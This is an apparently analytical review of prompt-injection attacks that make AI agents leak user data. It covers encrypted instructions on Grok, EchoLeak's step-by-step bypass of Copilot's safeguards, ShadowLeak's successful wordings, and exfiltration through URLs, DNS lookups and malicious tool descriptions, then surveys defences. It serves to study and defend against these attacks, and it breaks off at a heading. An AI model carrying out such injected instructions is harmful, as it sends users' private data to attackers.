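Models can often decode Base64 and simple ciphers that replace each letter with another, because the web pages and code they learned from contain many examples. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (Rall, Bauer and colleagues, 2025) describes how an earlier jailbreaking method, CipherChat, exploited this ability. Its users put forbidden requests into Morse code or a Caesar cipher, which shifts every letter by a fixed number of places. Models often decoded the requests and answered them, apparently because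 their safety training had used mostly ordinary text.

A simple encoding can in principle get past the model's own safeguards as well as a filter. This works only within a narrow range of ability, where the model can decode the text well enough to act on it but does not recognise the result as something to refuse. Base64 was more useful to attackers when models' training covered it less well.

### Text that appears when an image shrinks

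Large pictures take a lot of computing power to process, so many products shrink them before passing them to the model. The user sees the original, but the model receives the smaller copy. An attacker can prepare a picture containing written instructions that are legible only in the smaller copy.

The simplest method of shrinking a picture, nearest-neighbour scaling, keeps some pixels and discards the rest. Reducing a picture from 4,000 by 4,000 pixels to 1,000 by 1,000 keeps one pixel in every sixteen. An attacker who knows which pixels are kept can control the entire copy by changing about 6% of the original. The altered pixels are scattered among unaltered ones, which makes them hard to notice at full size, especially in a dark or busy part of the picture. Smoother methods compute each new pixel as a weighted average of several old ones, so the attacker must do more calculation to find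 values that produce the intended average.

The security company Trail of Bits demonstrated such attacks in August 2025 on Google's Gemini, among other products. Unlike the altered pictures in *Imprompter*, the small copy contains real words, which the model reads like any other text in a picture. The attacker needs to know how the product resizes pictures, but doesn't need the model's weights.

This also makes the disguise easy to remove. The words become visible if the product shows the user the same small copy that the model receives. A filter can find them by checking the picture after resizing, but it may miss them if it checks only the original.

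### Encryption and the attack on Grok

Encryption hides an instruction more thoroughly than Base64, which a model can decode itself and a filter can decode with a few lines of code. Decrypting a modern cipher such as AES-256 takes thousands of exact calculations. A language model can't do these by predicting tokens, so it needs a code tool even if it has the key.

Adversa AI's *Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026) describes an attack that exploits this. Adversa AI is a security company, and its target was the web version of Grok, the chat agent from Elon Musk's company xAI. The attack goes roughly like this:

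1. The user asks Grok to summarise a web page that the attacker has prepared.
2. The page contains encrypted text, the material for the key and a request to decrypt the text with Python. A filter that classifies the wording finds nothing harmful in the encrypted part.
3. Grok decrypts the text in its own code environment, and the attacker's instructions come back as the output of that program.
4. Following the instructions, Grok collects the user's name, approximate location and subscription tier, along with everything the user has typed in the conversation.
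5. Grok puts this data into a web address and opens the address with its browsing tool, which sends the data to the attacker's server.

In Adversa AI's demonstration, the user saw no warning or confirmation request. SecurityWeek's *Encrypted Prompts Bypass AI Safety Guardrails in Grok and Gemini* (2026) compares the web version of the attack to a watering hole, the security term for a site booby-trapped to attack its visitors. The attacker may still have to persuade people to ask Grok about the page, but the attack then requires no further clicks.

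The page also includes a hint about how to decode the hidden text, which Graves's outside attacker lacked. Graves put the hints in the system prompt, whereas on Grok the untrusted page itself contained the request to decrypt, and the agent carried it out.

Adversa AI argues that the agent then trusts the decrypted text more than it would trust the same words on a web page, because the text arrives as the result of its own program. This is plausible, but the company infers it from the agent's behaviour and reports no test with the same instructions in plain text on the page. There is also some reason to doubt it, because Ye and colleagues found that a text's style affects how a model represents it much more than its label does, although they tested different models. The encryption may have helped only by getting the instructions past Grok's filter.

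The demonstration also doesn't establish that the cipher had to be strong. Adversa AI acknowledges that a weaker encoding might pass a particular product's filter too. Quanta Magazine explains that filters have to be smaller and faster than the models they protect, so a puzzle that is easy for the model may be too hard for the filter. The advantage of AES-256 is that the attacker doesn't have to guess what the filter can decode.

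The attack did not work reliably. The AI Downside's *Grok Can Leak Your Chat History to a Web Page* (2026) reports a success rate of roughly 40% in about 20 attempts since June and attributes the figure to Adversa AI, whose own post doesn't mention it. The AI Downside is an anonymous blog, so the figure deserves some caution. Even if the figure is right, the true rate could easily be anywhere from 20% to 60% because there were so few attempts. The exact rate hardly matters to an attacker, since a popular page might receive thousands of visits.

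Adversa AI reported the attack to xAI on 3 June 2026. xAI acknowledged the report but gave no details and no date for a fix, and it didn't answer further messages on 4 and 10 August. The attack still worked on 19 August. Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) reported the next day that Grok was still leaking the data, and The AI Downside described the flaw as unpatched on 26 August. SpaceX, which had acquired xAI earlier in the year, did not respond to questions for The Register's *Grok chat duped into swallowing injected instructions*. The latest published reports on the flaw date from August 2026, so it isn't publicly known whether xAI has fixed it since.

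xAI had received similar warnings before. Embrace The Red's *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, a 2024 post on a security blog, covered invisible text as well as a leak through images that Grok loaded from outside servers in the iPhone app of the social network X. Willison, in a post also titled *Security ProbLLMs in xAI's Grok*, criticised the company for closing all of the reports as "Informational", which in practice means that it did not regard them as flaws to fix.

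Adversa AI also tried encrypted instructions on Google's Gemini, where they produced a jailbreak but no theft. The decrypted text imitated an error message and led Gemini to write instructions for an incendiary weapon, which it then encrypted so that the filter on its answers received only ciphertext. Rony Utevsky, the company's lead researcher, told The Register that the theft doesn't work on Gemini because Python programs there can't contact outside websites. This explanation seems incomplete, since on Grok the data left through the browsing tool, not Python. The success rate on Gemini had fallen sharply by August, and Adversa AI couldn't determine why.

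Utevsky thinks an attacker could also split an instruction across several encrypted fragments or web pages, each meaningless until the agent's program joins them. Adversa AI hasn't demonstrated this. The company sells a product that monitors coding agents for such attacks, so it has an interest in making them sound formidable, but the account of how the original attack works is detailed.

### Disguised and undisguised instructions compared

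The demonstration on Grok can't show whether the disguise made the theft more likely, because it had no plain version for comparison. Rall and colleagues ran such a comparison on more than two dozen models. They built an agent with two tools, one for searching a company's internal documents and one for fetching web pages. The documents contained a secret about a fictional "Project Alpha". A user asked the agent to summarise a blog post in which the researchers had hidden an instruction to look up the secret and request a web address containing it. The attempt counted as a success if the secret appeared in the researchers' server log.

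The tests started with 89 templates, many of which were well-known ways of wrapping a malicious instruction, such as in a role-play. Each template had 12 versions, the original and 11 alterations, for a total of 1,068 attempts per model. The alterations included rewording, translation into Hindi, Base64, binary digits, emoji, random capital letters and scattered invisible characters.

The original attacks worked best, succeeding just over 12% of the time across all models. Adding a few control codes for text terminals to the front, which hardly changes the text, worked almost as well. The further an alteration moved from the original wording, the less often it worked. Base64 mostly failed, though it had worked against earlier models, and binary and emoji also did very badly.

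Rall and colleagues conclude that models now reliably detect Base64, but their experiment can't quite establish this because it records only whether the secret reached the attacker. A model that decoded the instruction and refused would produce the same result as one that decoded it wrongly or took the string for clutter on the page. For binary, they favour failed decoding as the explanation and suggest that no model could decode it unaided.

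The agent in this study had no code tool. Graves's zero-width scheme also encodes instructions in binary, using invisible characters as digits, and GPT-5.2 followed most of them when it had Python and a hint. The models and tasks differ, but the results are consistent with binary failing because the agent had no decoder, not because the models recognised an attack.

The differences between models were larger than those between disguises:

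| Model | Successful attempts, all versions |
| --- | --- |
| Grok 4 | 72.4% |
| Mercury | 29.1% |
| Qwen3 235B | 28.3% |
| Llama 4 Scout | 14.8% |
| Claude 3 Haiku | 6.0% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 1.9% |
| GPT-5-nano | 0.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 0.0% |

Model size doesn't explain the differences in vulnerability. Qwen3, with 235 billion parameters, was far more vulnerable than DeepSeek V3.1, with 685 billion, and some small models leaked nothing. Models from the same company tended to behave alike, which suggests that training is the cause. In the full results, Grok 4 alone accounts for about a third of all successful attempts, so the ranking of the disguises mostly reflects what worked on Grok 4 and a handful of other vulnerable models.

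The study may underestimate how much disguises help an attacker, for two reasons. Rall and colleagues tried each version only once, whereas an attacker can repeat a promising one. More importantly, their agent had no filter, so a disguise only had to get past the model. They acknowledge this and expect disguises to become useful once a product has other security layers.

The supposedly undisguised templates were already hidden from the user as white text on a white background. This doesn't make the attack less reliable, because the agent receives the same text whatever its colour. An attacker who only wants to deceive the user therefore doesn't need to encode an instruction on a web page. This does not hold when the victim has to copy the text and paste it into a chat, as in *Imprompter*, because white text becomes visible there.

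### Theft that looks like routine work

An attacker can also leave the instruction readable but disguise its purpose. *The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) compared overt requests for a secret with requests that present the same leak as an ordinary technical step.

The researchers gave an agent a made-up secret token and a rule against sending it anywhere except one trusted address. The agent then had to summarise a web page written by the attacker. Its tools were dummies that only recorded what the model tried to send. For every attack, the researchers also ran the agent on a clean version of the page. They counted the attack as successful only if the agent kept the secret on the clean page and leaked it on the attacker's page.

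The first set had ten kinds of attack, including direct commands, text hidden in the page's code, claims of urgency and Base64. OpenAI's GPT-4o leaked nothing in 200 trials. Concealment again made a vulnerable model less likely to comply. The small open model Llama 3.1 8B obeyed the direct command 70% of the time, but never the hidden or Base64 version.

For the second set, Rahman and Kim reworded one of the overt attacks. Some pages presented the token as a value that a form or configuration file required. Others gave the attacker's server a name resembling the trusted one. GPT-4o now leaked the token in all 20 trials with a page that called it an "integrity signature" (a code for checking that data has arrived unaltered) and in all 20 with a page that called it a configuration value. Across the whole set, including the original attack as a baseline, it leaked the token in 40% of trials.

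GPT-4o attached the secret to its summary as though it were a checksum. The page contained no explicit request to disclose anything, so the model apparently did not apply the rule about disclosure. The rule seems to have had very little effect anyway. When Rahman and Kim removed it, GPT-4o still ignored all the overt attacks, and its leak rate on the reworded ones rose only from 31.9% to 38.1%, a difference no larger than they saw between identical runs.

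The page's wording had more effect. In one experiment, the researchers kept a successful page and changed only the name of the field meant to hold the token. With the original name, "signature", the agent leaked the token in 10 out of 10 trials. With names that suggested a password or another credential, it leaked nothing in 20 trials, and with neutral technical names it leaked the token in 10 out of 40. The model seems to have become cautious because of the mention of credentials rather than the request for the secret that the rule protected.

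Small changes of wording also greatly affect the success rate. Five paraphrases of the signature page succeeded between 0% and 100% of the time, with an average of 52%. Rahman and Kim calculate that an attacker who tried three of them would have about a 96% chance of at least one success. That figure understates the difficulty of the attack because it assumes the attacker already has a page that works. When the researchers wrote 13 new framings from scratch, all 130 trials failed. The framings also don't carry over well between models. The configuration page that always worked on GPT-4o never worked on GPT-4o-mini, while a page presenting the token as a login detail succeeded 0% of the time on GPT-4o and 85% on GPT-4o-mini.

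The models are old by the standards of late 2026, and the agent took only one step, so these rates are weak evidence about current products. On the ChatGPT website, the same kind of page produced no leaks in 48 trials. Rahman and Kim can't tell whether a filter, a different model or something else prevented them. They also looked for the secret only in ChatGPT's reply and didn't connect a tool that could have sent it out. But Hofer and colleagues saw a similar pattern on the newer GPT-5, where ordinary-looking content worked better than blunt commands.

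### When a disguise is worth the cost

In *Imprompter*, by contrast, the best disguised prompt was more reliable than the plain one, because the search that produced the gibberish had already selected it for reliability. Base64 is a mechanical conversion that isn't tailored to the model, and each decoding step adds a chance of error.

Encoding an instruction mainly serves to conceal it, and usually makes the attack less reliable. An attacker can make up for the lost reliability by optimising the text, or by choosing an agent with a code tool, which decodes exactly. The tool helps only if the agent decides to use it, as Graves's low rates without hints show. Whether encoding is worthwhile depends on the defences the attacker faces. If a product's filter blocks every readable version, even a 40% success rate is a large improvement on zero, but if the agent has no filter, encrypting the instruction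 adds several steps that can fail and gains nothing over white text.

A theft worded as routine work gets past the model doing the user's task, but the text remains open to inspection. When Rahman and Kim gave a second model 80 reworded pages and told it exactly what kinds of request to look for, it flagged all of them. Encryption, by contrast, may hide the instruction from the filter, but the agent's model still receives it in full after decrypting it and can refuse.

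The attack on Grok combined the two. Once decrypted, the instructions told the agent to construct a further "decryption key", which was really a template for the user's name, location and conversation. Opening a web address containing that "key" then looked like one more step in reading the page. Adversa AI didn't test the encryption and the false key separately, so it is unclear how much each contributed. Grok 4 had followed most of Rall and colleagues' instructions without encryption, which suggests that the cipher was useful mainly against the filter rather than the model.

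## By what routes has data left real products?

On Grok, the stolen data left through the agent's browsing tool. Researchers have also got data out of commercial agents through links, images and lookups of server names, and, in laboratory tests, through the parameters of a malicious tool. The route determines whose computer sends the data, and therefore who could notice or block the theft.

### Links and images in the answer

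Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions from their company's emails, files and chats. It searches these sources for passages related to the question and puts them into the model's context. Outsiders can't use a company's Copilot, but they can email its staff. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes how a single email could make Copilot send company data to an outside server. Ravia's team, then the research department of the company Aim Security and now called Cato AI Labs, got past Microsoft's safeguards one at a time:

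1. Microsoft screened incoming text with a classifier trained to recognise prompt injections. The researchers worded their instructions as if for the person receiving the email and never mentioned AI, and the classifier let them through.
2. Copilot reads an email only if it seems relevant to the employee's question. The researchers therefore wrote one long email with sections on many office topics, such as onboarding and leave, and repeated the instructions in each.
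3. The instructions were to take the most sensitive information in the context and put it into a link to the researchers' server. Copilot deletes links to outside sites before the user can click them, but it overlooked a less common Markdown notation in which the address stands apart from the link. An employee who clicked would have sent off the data.
4. To do without the click, the researchers used the same notation for an image. Copilot let it through, but the browser blocked it, because Microsoft's page allows images only from a list of approved sites.
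5. One approved site, part of Microsoft Teams, turned out to fetch any other address on request. The browser requested the image from Teams, and Teams contacted the researchers' server, using an address that contained the data.

The email also asked its supposed recipient never to mention it, giving compliance as the reason, and Copilot then left the email out of the sources it cited.

EchoLeak could reach anything in the model's context, including the whole conversation and any emails or files Copilot had retrieved. The attacker couldn't pick a particular document, though, and the leaked data would have depended largely on what the employee had asked about.

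Willison (2025) described EchoLeak as an extended variant of an attack already seen in a dozen products. Ravia's claim that EchoLeak was a first is narrower than the title suggests. In earlier attacks, the user had to point the agent at the attacker's text, or the attacker could extract only very limited data. With EchoLeak, the attacker's email only had to be in the mailbox when the employee asked a suitable question.

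Microsoft patched EchoLeak, but in December 2026 *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) described three new zero-click attacks on the same product, also from Cato AI Labs. Like EchoLeak, each starts with an email that the victim never opens. *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (AIAIAI.FYI, 2026) reports that the data left through an image address, a link to a saved file or code, and that a documented block on outbound traffic from Microsoft's sandbox failed. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the researchers as saying that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak.

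### Pages the agent fetches itself

When data leaves through an image link, the user's browser sends the request, and the vendor's page or the employer's security software may block it. A browsing tool usually sends its requests from the vendor's servers, so the employer never sees them.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes such an attack on Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that reads sources, writes a report and can be connected to a user's Gmail. Radware, a security company, sent a test mailbox an email about a staff restructuring, with instructions that an attacker could hide in tiny or white text. The mailbox also held a realistic message containing an employee's name and address. When the user asked for research on the day's emails, the agent read both messages, put the name and address into a URL and opened it, without anything appearing on the user's screen.

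Radware needed several attempts to get this far:

- A direct request to send the data to an outside address failed, as did one that claimed to come from the user. The agent treated the address as suspicious and searched for it on the web without opening it.
- Naming the browsing tool explicitly sometimes made the agent try the address, but the request often failed.
- Blaming the failures on the internet connection and asking for several retries worked more often. Even then, the agent sometimes opened the address without the personal data.
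- Asking the agent to convert the data to Base64 first, supposedly to keep it secure, worked every time in repeated tests. Radware doesn't say how many tests it ran.

OpenAI restricted the addresses from which ChatGPT would load images, but Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses that Deep Research could open. An attacker could therefore send data out without the approved site that EchoLeak needed to pass it on.

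The August 2026 attack on Copilot Personal, Microsoft's assistant for consumers, used the same kind of channel but a different entry point. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes a link to the genuine Copilot website with a prompt written into the address. Such links normally only fill in the text box, and the user has to press Enter. An undocumented parameter made Copilot run the prompt as soon as the page loaded and finish running it even if the victim closed the tab. Copilot could search whatever the victim had connected to it, such as Gmail, Google Drive or a calendar. In one test, it retrieved an email containing a password in plain text. It then encoded the email's text, put it into a web address and fetched that address with its page-summarising tool.

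CoSnitch starts with the victim's click, whereas in the link version of EchoLeak the click sends the data out. CoSnitch is also unusual because Copilot processed the attacker's prompt as if the victim had typed it, so training a model to give web pages and emails less authority than the user would not have helped.

Varonis, a data security company, learned about the undocumented parameter by repeatedly asking Copilot why a prompt couldn't run automatically. One of Copilot's explanations listed the parameters that Microsoft had supposedly disabled. SC Media's *New attack bypasses AI guardrails by encrypting malicious prompts* (2026) places the password theft in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the business product, but Varonis names Copilot Personal.

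The business product had a similar flaw. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes another Varonis attack, in which one click on a link exposed emails, meeting details, company files and one-time login codes. The Next Web reports that Microsoft rated it critical, although it scored only 6.5 out of 10 on the standard severity scale because the victim has to click.

*Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, by the security company PromptArmor, describes an attack on Rovo, the agent in Atlassian's office software. The victim uploads a guide found online, which contains hidden instructions, and asks Rovo to organise some tickets in Jira, Atlassian's system for tracking work. Rovo collects tickets and documents, adds their contents to the attacker's web address and opens the resulting address. PromptArmor found that Rovo's tool would open any address, including one the agent had just composed,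 without asking the user for approval. A user who returned to the chat later saw the suggested changes to the tickets but no trace of the theft.

The attack on Rovo worked even after an administrator switched off web search for the whole organisation. The setting removed the search tool but left the separate tool that opens the results. Rovo also displayed Markdown images, so data could still have leaked through them if only the browsing route had been closed.

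### Why encoding the data helps it get out

Leak-detection software often searches outgoing text for recognisable patterns, such as the @ sign in an email address, the length of a payment card number, or the known letters that begin many access keys. Encoding removes these patterns. In Base64, Ada Moreno's phone number, 5550142, becomes `NTU1MDE0Mg==`, which a filter for phone numbers would not match.

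A filter that decodes Base64 before checking could still miss the data if the attacker asks the agent to reverse the text first, use a different encoding or spread the data over several requests. An agent with a code tool could also encrypt it. Blocking every string that the filter can't interpret is impractical because ordinary web addresses often contain random-looking identifiers. Checking the destination avoids these problems because the address must still lead to a server from which the attacker can collect the data.

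Varonis says that one reason for encoding the data in CoSnitch is to get past filters for passwords and keys. It also wrongly says that Base64 compresses the data, when it makes text about a third longer.

Radware's more specific explanation for ShadowLeak is that the model encoded the name and address before it wrote the tool call, so the software that executes the call received only a harmless-looking string. This fits the sequence of failures and successes, but Radware could observe the system only from outside. The instruction also described the encoding as a way to protect the data, which may have made the model more likely to comply. Telling the two explanations apart would require a test of the encoding without that justification, and Radware does not report one.

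Rall and colleagues found that encoding an attacker's instruction usually makes it less reliable, because the model has to decode it before acting. Encoding the stolen data avoids this problem, since the model receives the instruction in plain language and the attacker does the decoding. A model without a code tool could still make mistakes when encoding a long text, but they are less likely with something as short as a name and address.

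### Lookups of a server's name

Before a computer can connect to `pictures.example`, it has to look up the server's numerical address in the domain name system (DNS). If no nearby computer has stored the answer, the query goes to a name server chosen by the domain's owner. An attacker who owns the domain can therefore receive data in the name being looked up. A lookup of `ada-moreno.pictures.example` delivers the user's name to the attacker's name server, even if the computer never requests a page or picture. A full domain name can have only about 250 characters, so sending more data takes many lookups.

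Researchers at the security company Zenity used DNS to get data out of Agentforce, Salesforce's agents for sales and customer service. *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026) reports that the attack, called SalesBleed, begins with a form on a company's public website that adds prospective customers' details directly to the company's customer database. The attacker, who needs no account with Salesforce or the company, enters hidden instructions in the form. When an employee's agent later processes the record, it looks up other customers and sends out their data.

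In the demonstration, the data consisted of company names and deal sizes. According to Zenity, an attacker could have used the instructions to request any data the agent's database tool could reach, which typically includes accounts and contacts.

Salesforce already had a control, Trusted URLs, that was supposed to remove untrusted web addresses from the agent's output, but SalesBleed got around it. Salesforce fixed the problem by closing this gap, which suggests that the lookup came from an address the control should have removed.

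### Data handed to a malicious tool

An attacker can also supply the tool that sends the data out. Many agents let users install other people's tools from public platforms. The model uses each tool's name and description to decide which to call and how to fill in its parameters. If the tool belongs to the attacker, its code can send those parameters anywhere.

A malicious tool often receives only what the model writes into the tool call, so the attacker has to make the model include private information there. Jia, Wang and colleagues (2026) found in *ContextLeak* that the tool's name and description can do this without an obvious command. The description presents the tool as a normal part of every task, so that the model selects it often, and presents the user's information as necessary for correct results. For example, a tool described as keeping answers consistent has an apparent reason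 to require the whole conversation.

Jia and colleagues trained a language model to write such descriptions by reinforcement learning. They simulated users, each with a request, a conversation and a set of harmless tools, and added the malicious tool to each set. The model received a higher reward when the agent chose the malicious tool and when the parameters it passed closely matched the user's private context. The model also received hints drawn from patterns in earlier attempts. The attacker needs to know which agent the victim uses and to run a copy of it, but doesn't need to know which language model the victim's copy uses.

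The method extracted users' requests, conversations and lists of installed tools more effectively than six existing attacks adapted for comparison. It also worked when the victims' conversations differed substantially from the simulated ones. Filters that look for malicious instructions in tool descriptions were insufficient, partly because the attack's descriptions contain no overt instructions. Models trained to resist manipulated descriptions became worse at choosing legitimate tools.

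Even a list of installed tools can help an attacker, since it may reveal the user's job or employer. But the victim must first install the malicious tool. The study used simulated users, so it doesn't show how often real people would install it or how much private data a real campaign would collect.

The attack meets all three of Willison's conditions with a single tool. The tool's description is the untrusted content, the conversation holds the private data, and the call to the tool sends that data out. An agent could therefore leak the conversation without ever opening a web page or an email.

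### Which personal data agents gave up in a simulated bank

The product demonstrations involve only a few pieces of data, chosen by the researchers, so they are weak evidence of which kinds of data an agent will protect. *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (Alizadeh, Samei et al., 2025) tested this with a fictional bank customer in AgentDojo. During each of 16 ordinary banking tasks, the agent encountered a message, written as if by the customer, with a request to email personal data to an outside address.

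The researchers tested six models with four versions of this message, each requesting different data: the account balance and address in one, the password alone in another, and the password with one or two other details in the remaining two. An attack counted as successful if any sensitive item leaked. Averaged over the four versions, attacks succeeded in about 20% of attempts against most models and in 40% against Llama 4.

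The message's success depended heavily on the type of data it requested. It succeeded 93% of the time on Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 55% on Llama 4 when it didn't mention a password, but requests for only the password failed every time on every model except Llama 4. Models often refused to reveal the password but supplied the other details in the same reply. A typical reply gave the balance and the city, then explained that sharing a password would be a security risk.

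Models sometimes leaked passwords when the message also asked for other details. With one additional detail, GPT-3.5 leaked the password in 18.75% of attempts (three of 16 tasks) and Llama 4 in 12.5%, while the other models leaked none. With two additional details, four of the six models leaked a password at least once, but GPT-3.5 leaked none. These results suggest that surrounding a sensitive request with ordinary ones can weaken a refusal, but the numbers are too small to show by how much.

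Alizadeh and colleagues attributed the refusals to safety training and noticed particular caution around the word "password". Rahman and Kim later noticed similar caution around labels that suggested a credential. An attacker can often do without the word, because an address, a balance or the text of a private email may be valuable enough. In CoSnitch, Copilot retrieved and sent a password even though the prompt included a search of the mailbox for that word. The model may have been less cautious because the prompt appeared to come from the user and the password was just part of an email.

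In a larger set of 48 tasks, attacks succeeded about 15% of the time on average. Tasks in which the customer had asked the agent to look up data or authorise something were the most vulnerable, probably because the attacker's request resembled what the agent was already doing. The models tested are now old, so the percentages are a poor guide to current products.

### Vendors' fixes and evidence of criminal use

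Microsoft took about four months to patch EchoLeak, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, and about eight to patch CoSnitch. OpenAI fixed ShadowLeak in roughly seven weeks but didn't tell Radware until September 2025. Radware published its findings on 18 September, as Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft* reported. Reprompt, an earlier one-click attack by Varonis on Copilot Personal, is included here for comparison:

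| Attack | Product | Vendor informed | Fixed | Source for these dates |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| EchoLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | January 2025 | May 2025 | Infosecurity Magazine |
| ShadowLeak | ChatGPT Deep Research | 18 June 2025 | Early August 2025 | Radware |
| Reprompt | Copilot Personal | August 2025 | January 2026 | The Next Web |
| CoSnitch | Copilot Personal | December 2025 | 18 August 2026 | Varonis |
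| Rovo attack | Atlassian Rovo | 23 May 2026 | Still open over two months later | PromptArmor |
| SalesBleed | Salesforce Agentforce | June 2026 | 18 August 2026 | Poireault |
| ReLeak | Microsoft 365 Copilot | – | 17 September, 11 and 15 November 2026 | AIAIAI.FYI |

Atlassian assigned a case number to PromptArmor's findings on Rovo and thanked the researchers, but then ignored several follow-up messages. PromptArmor therefore published the findings.

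Salesforce's fix closed an outbound channel, as Mistral's had on LeChat. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, an account of further attacks on Copilot, explains why vendors tend to focus on such channels. Copilot meets the other two of Willison's conditions by default, which leaves the channel as "the only part of this system that is realistically enforceable". But an agent may have many channels, and ReLeak's three routes out of Copilot came after Microsoft had patched EchoLeak.

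Security researchers demonstrated all the attacks in the table, and none of the published accounts identifies a real victim. Microsoft said that no one had exploited EchoLeak in the wild, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*. Cato AI Labs knows of no exploitation of ReLeak, and Varonis has seen no evidence that anyone has exploited CoSnitch.

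Microsoft's statement is the strongest evidence because the company can search its own records, although it also has an interest in reassuring customers. The researchers can't see those records, so their statements mean only that they know of no case. A successful theft might also leave few traces. Varonis says the request that carried the password was indistinguishable on the network from Copilot's request for any other page.

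OpenAI's engineers see attempted thefts on ChatGPT, which is some evidence that people try such attacks, although some of the attempts may be researchers' tests. The security companies that publish the demonstrations mostly sell protection against such attacks. Their demonstrations show that an outsider could have taken data from these products, but do not show how often criminals have done so.

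## Can filters or training stop disguised instructions?

An agent that never receives the attacker's instruction, or ignores it, can safely keep its access to the inbox, the web and the company's files. The user therefore loses less than with defences that remove the agent's abilities. Stopping the attack at the input also protects every outbound channel at once, including undiscovered ones, whereas Microsoft has had to close Copilot's one after another. A disguise can even make an attack easier to detect, because ordinary emails don't contain 96 invisible characters in a row or a paragraph of gibberish.

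### Removing invisible characters

The runtime can delete invisible characters before it passes a text to the model, without having to judge what the text means or whether the sender is honest. If it deletes all of them, Graves's hidden instructions never reach the model and no hint or code tool can recover them, a certainty that few other defences against prompt injection offer.

Deleting all of them would damage some ordinary text, though. Persian spelling uses the zero-width non-joiner inside many words to keep neighbouring letters apart, and several Indian scripts use it to select the shape of a letter. The family emoji is a row of people linked by zero-width joiners, and without them it displays as separate people. Tag characters are obsolete in their original role, but the flag emoji for England, Scotland and Wales each consist of a black flag followed by tag characters that spell the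 region's code.

A product with international users therefore needs rules that depend on context. It could keep a non-joiner between two Persian letters, a joiner between two emoji, and tag characters that follow a black flag and spell a real region's code, and delete the rest. That leaves little room for a message, since no Persian word or emoji contains a long run of such characters. An attacker could still hide one binary digit at each permitted place in a long Persian text, but the model would have to collect the digits from throughout the text.

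The filter also has to run after other software has converted any numeric character codes into the characters they represent. A web page can contain an invisible character written as a visible numeric code, and a filter that runs before the conversion won't find it. Removing invisible characters defeats only this disguise, because white text, Base64 and gibberish consist of characters that the filter has to let through.

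### Perplexity filters

Gibberish stands out because its characters come in an unlikely order. Perplexity measures this. For a text of *N* tokens, it is the exponential of the average negative log-probability per token:

$$\text{perplexity} = \exp\left(-\frac{1}{N}\sum_{i=1}^{N}\log P(t_i \mid t_1,\dots,t_{i-1})\right)$$

*P* is the probability that a language model gives to each token, given the tokens before it. If the model gives every token in a text a probability of one in ten, the text's perplexity is 10, as if the model were choosing among ten equally likely tokens each time. On the model that Fu and colleagues used, ordinary English scored below 10 and their best prompt for extracting personal data scored in the thousands, so the gap seems wide enough for a filter to tell them apart.

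But an average over a long text hides a short stretch of gibberish. Suppose an email has 1,000 tokens, of which 60 are a disguised prompt with a perplexity of 5,413 and the other 940 are ordinary text with a perplexity of 10. The whole email then scores:

$$\exp\left(\frac{60\ln 5413 + 940\ln 10}{1000}\right) = \exp(2.68) \approx 15$$

A harmless email with a few unusual names could easily score 15. Filters therefore slide a short window along the text and score each window separately. A 100-token window that contains the whole prompt scores about 437, while the windows around it stay near 10.

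Short windows can also raise the scores of harmless but unusual text, such as a list of part numbers, a tracking code or a few lines in a language the scoring model handles poorly. An office agent reads such text every day.

Fu and colleagues object that disguised prompts can have low perplexity and that harmless, computer-optimised prompts can have high perplexity. The second problem matters only to the extent that people use such prompts. The first is more serious, because an attacker who knows about the filter can add perplexity to the loss that the search minimises. The search then tends to pick replacements that read smoothly, but it has fewer tokens to choose from, so the prompts it finds may be less reliable.

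The filter still pushes attackers away from gibberish and towards readable text, which a wary user might recognise as an attack before pasting it into a chat. This helps little when the agent reads the text unsupervised, and Hofer and colleagues found that readable injections worked better than gibberish on GPT-5.

### Classifiers

A classifier can examine the meaning of readable text. Developers train a small language model on harmless texts and known attacks, and the runtime blocks any text that scores above a threshold. Anthropic, for example, scans incoming content for commands hidden in text, images or parts of a page's interface, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*.

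Choosing a threshold is difficult because agents read so much. If a classifier wrongly flags 1% of harmless texts, an agent that reads 200 emails a day loses two of them. Raising the threshold recovers those emails but lets more attacks through.

Some attacks also contain nothing that a classifier could safely treat as a warning sign. *The Attacker Moves Second* describes a note that got past a detector made by Protect AI. The note claimed that company policy required staff to log each rescheduled meeting by deleting a certain tracking file. A real company might have such a rule, and a classifier can't tell whether it does without knowing the company.

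### Training the model to rank its sources

Vendors also train the agent's own model to rank instructions by source. The developer's instructions come first, then the user's, and the model should not follow any instructions in text from web pages, emails or tools. According to PYMNTS, Anthropic does this with reinforcement learning, exposing Claude to injections in simulated web content and rewarding it when it identifies and refuses them.

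Training has an advantage over filters when the attacker disguises an instruction. The agent has to recover the instruction before acting on it, and a well-trained model can then recognise that it came from a stranger. Training could in principle work against every disguise, including ones nobody has invented yet.

Models learn the ranking imperfectly. Ye and colleagues found that they treat text written like a user's as a user's, whatever its label. The ranking also doesn't help when the attacker's text arrives in the user's own message. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reports results similar to or better than those of its predecessor, Opus 5, on every injection test. Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026) says the exception is text that people paste in themselves, which the new model resists less well. Anthropic's developer guide, *Prompting Claude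 Opus 5.5*, also lists pasted text among the model's differences from Opus 5.

Imprompter relies on this route. Better ranking could partly explain the result, because a model that has learned to trust the user more than web pages may extend that trust to everything in the user's message. But Anthropic could also have changed something else in training that explains it.

### Attackers who adapt

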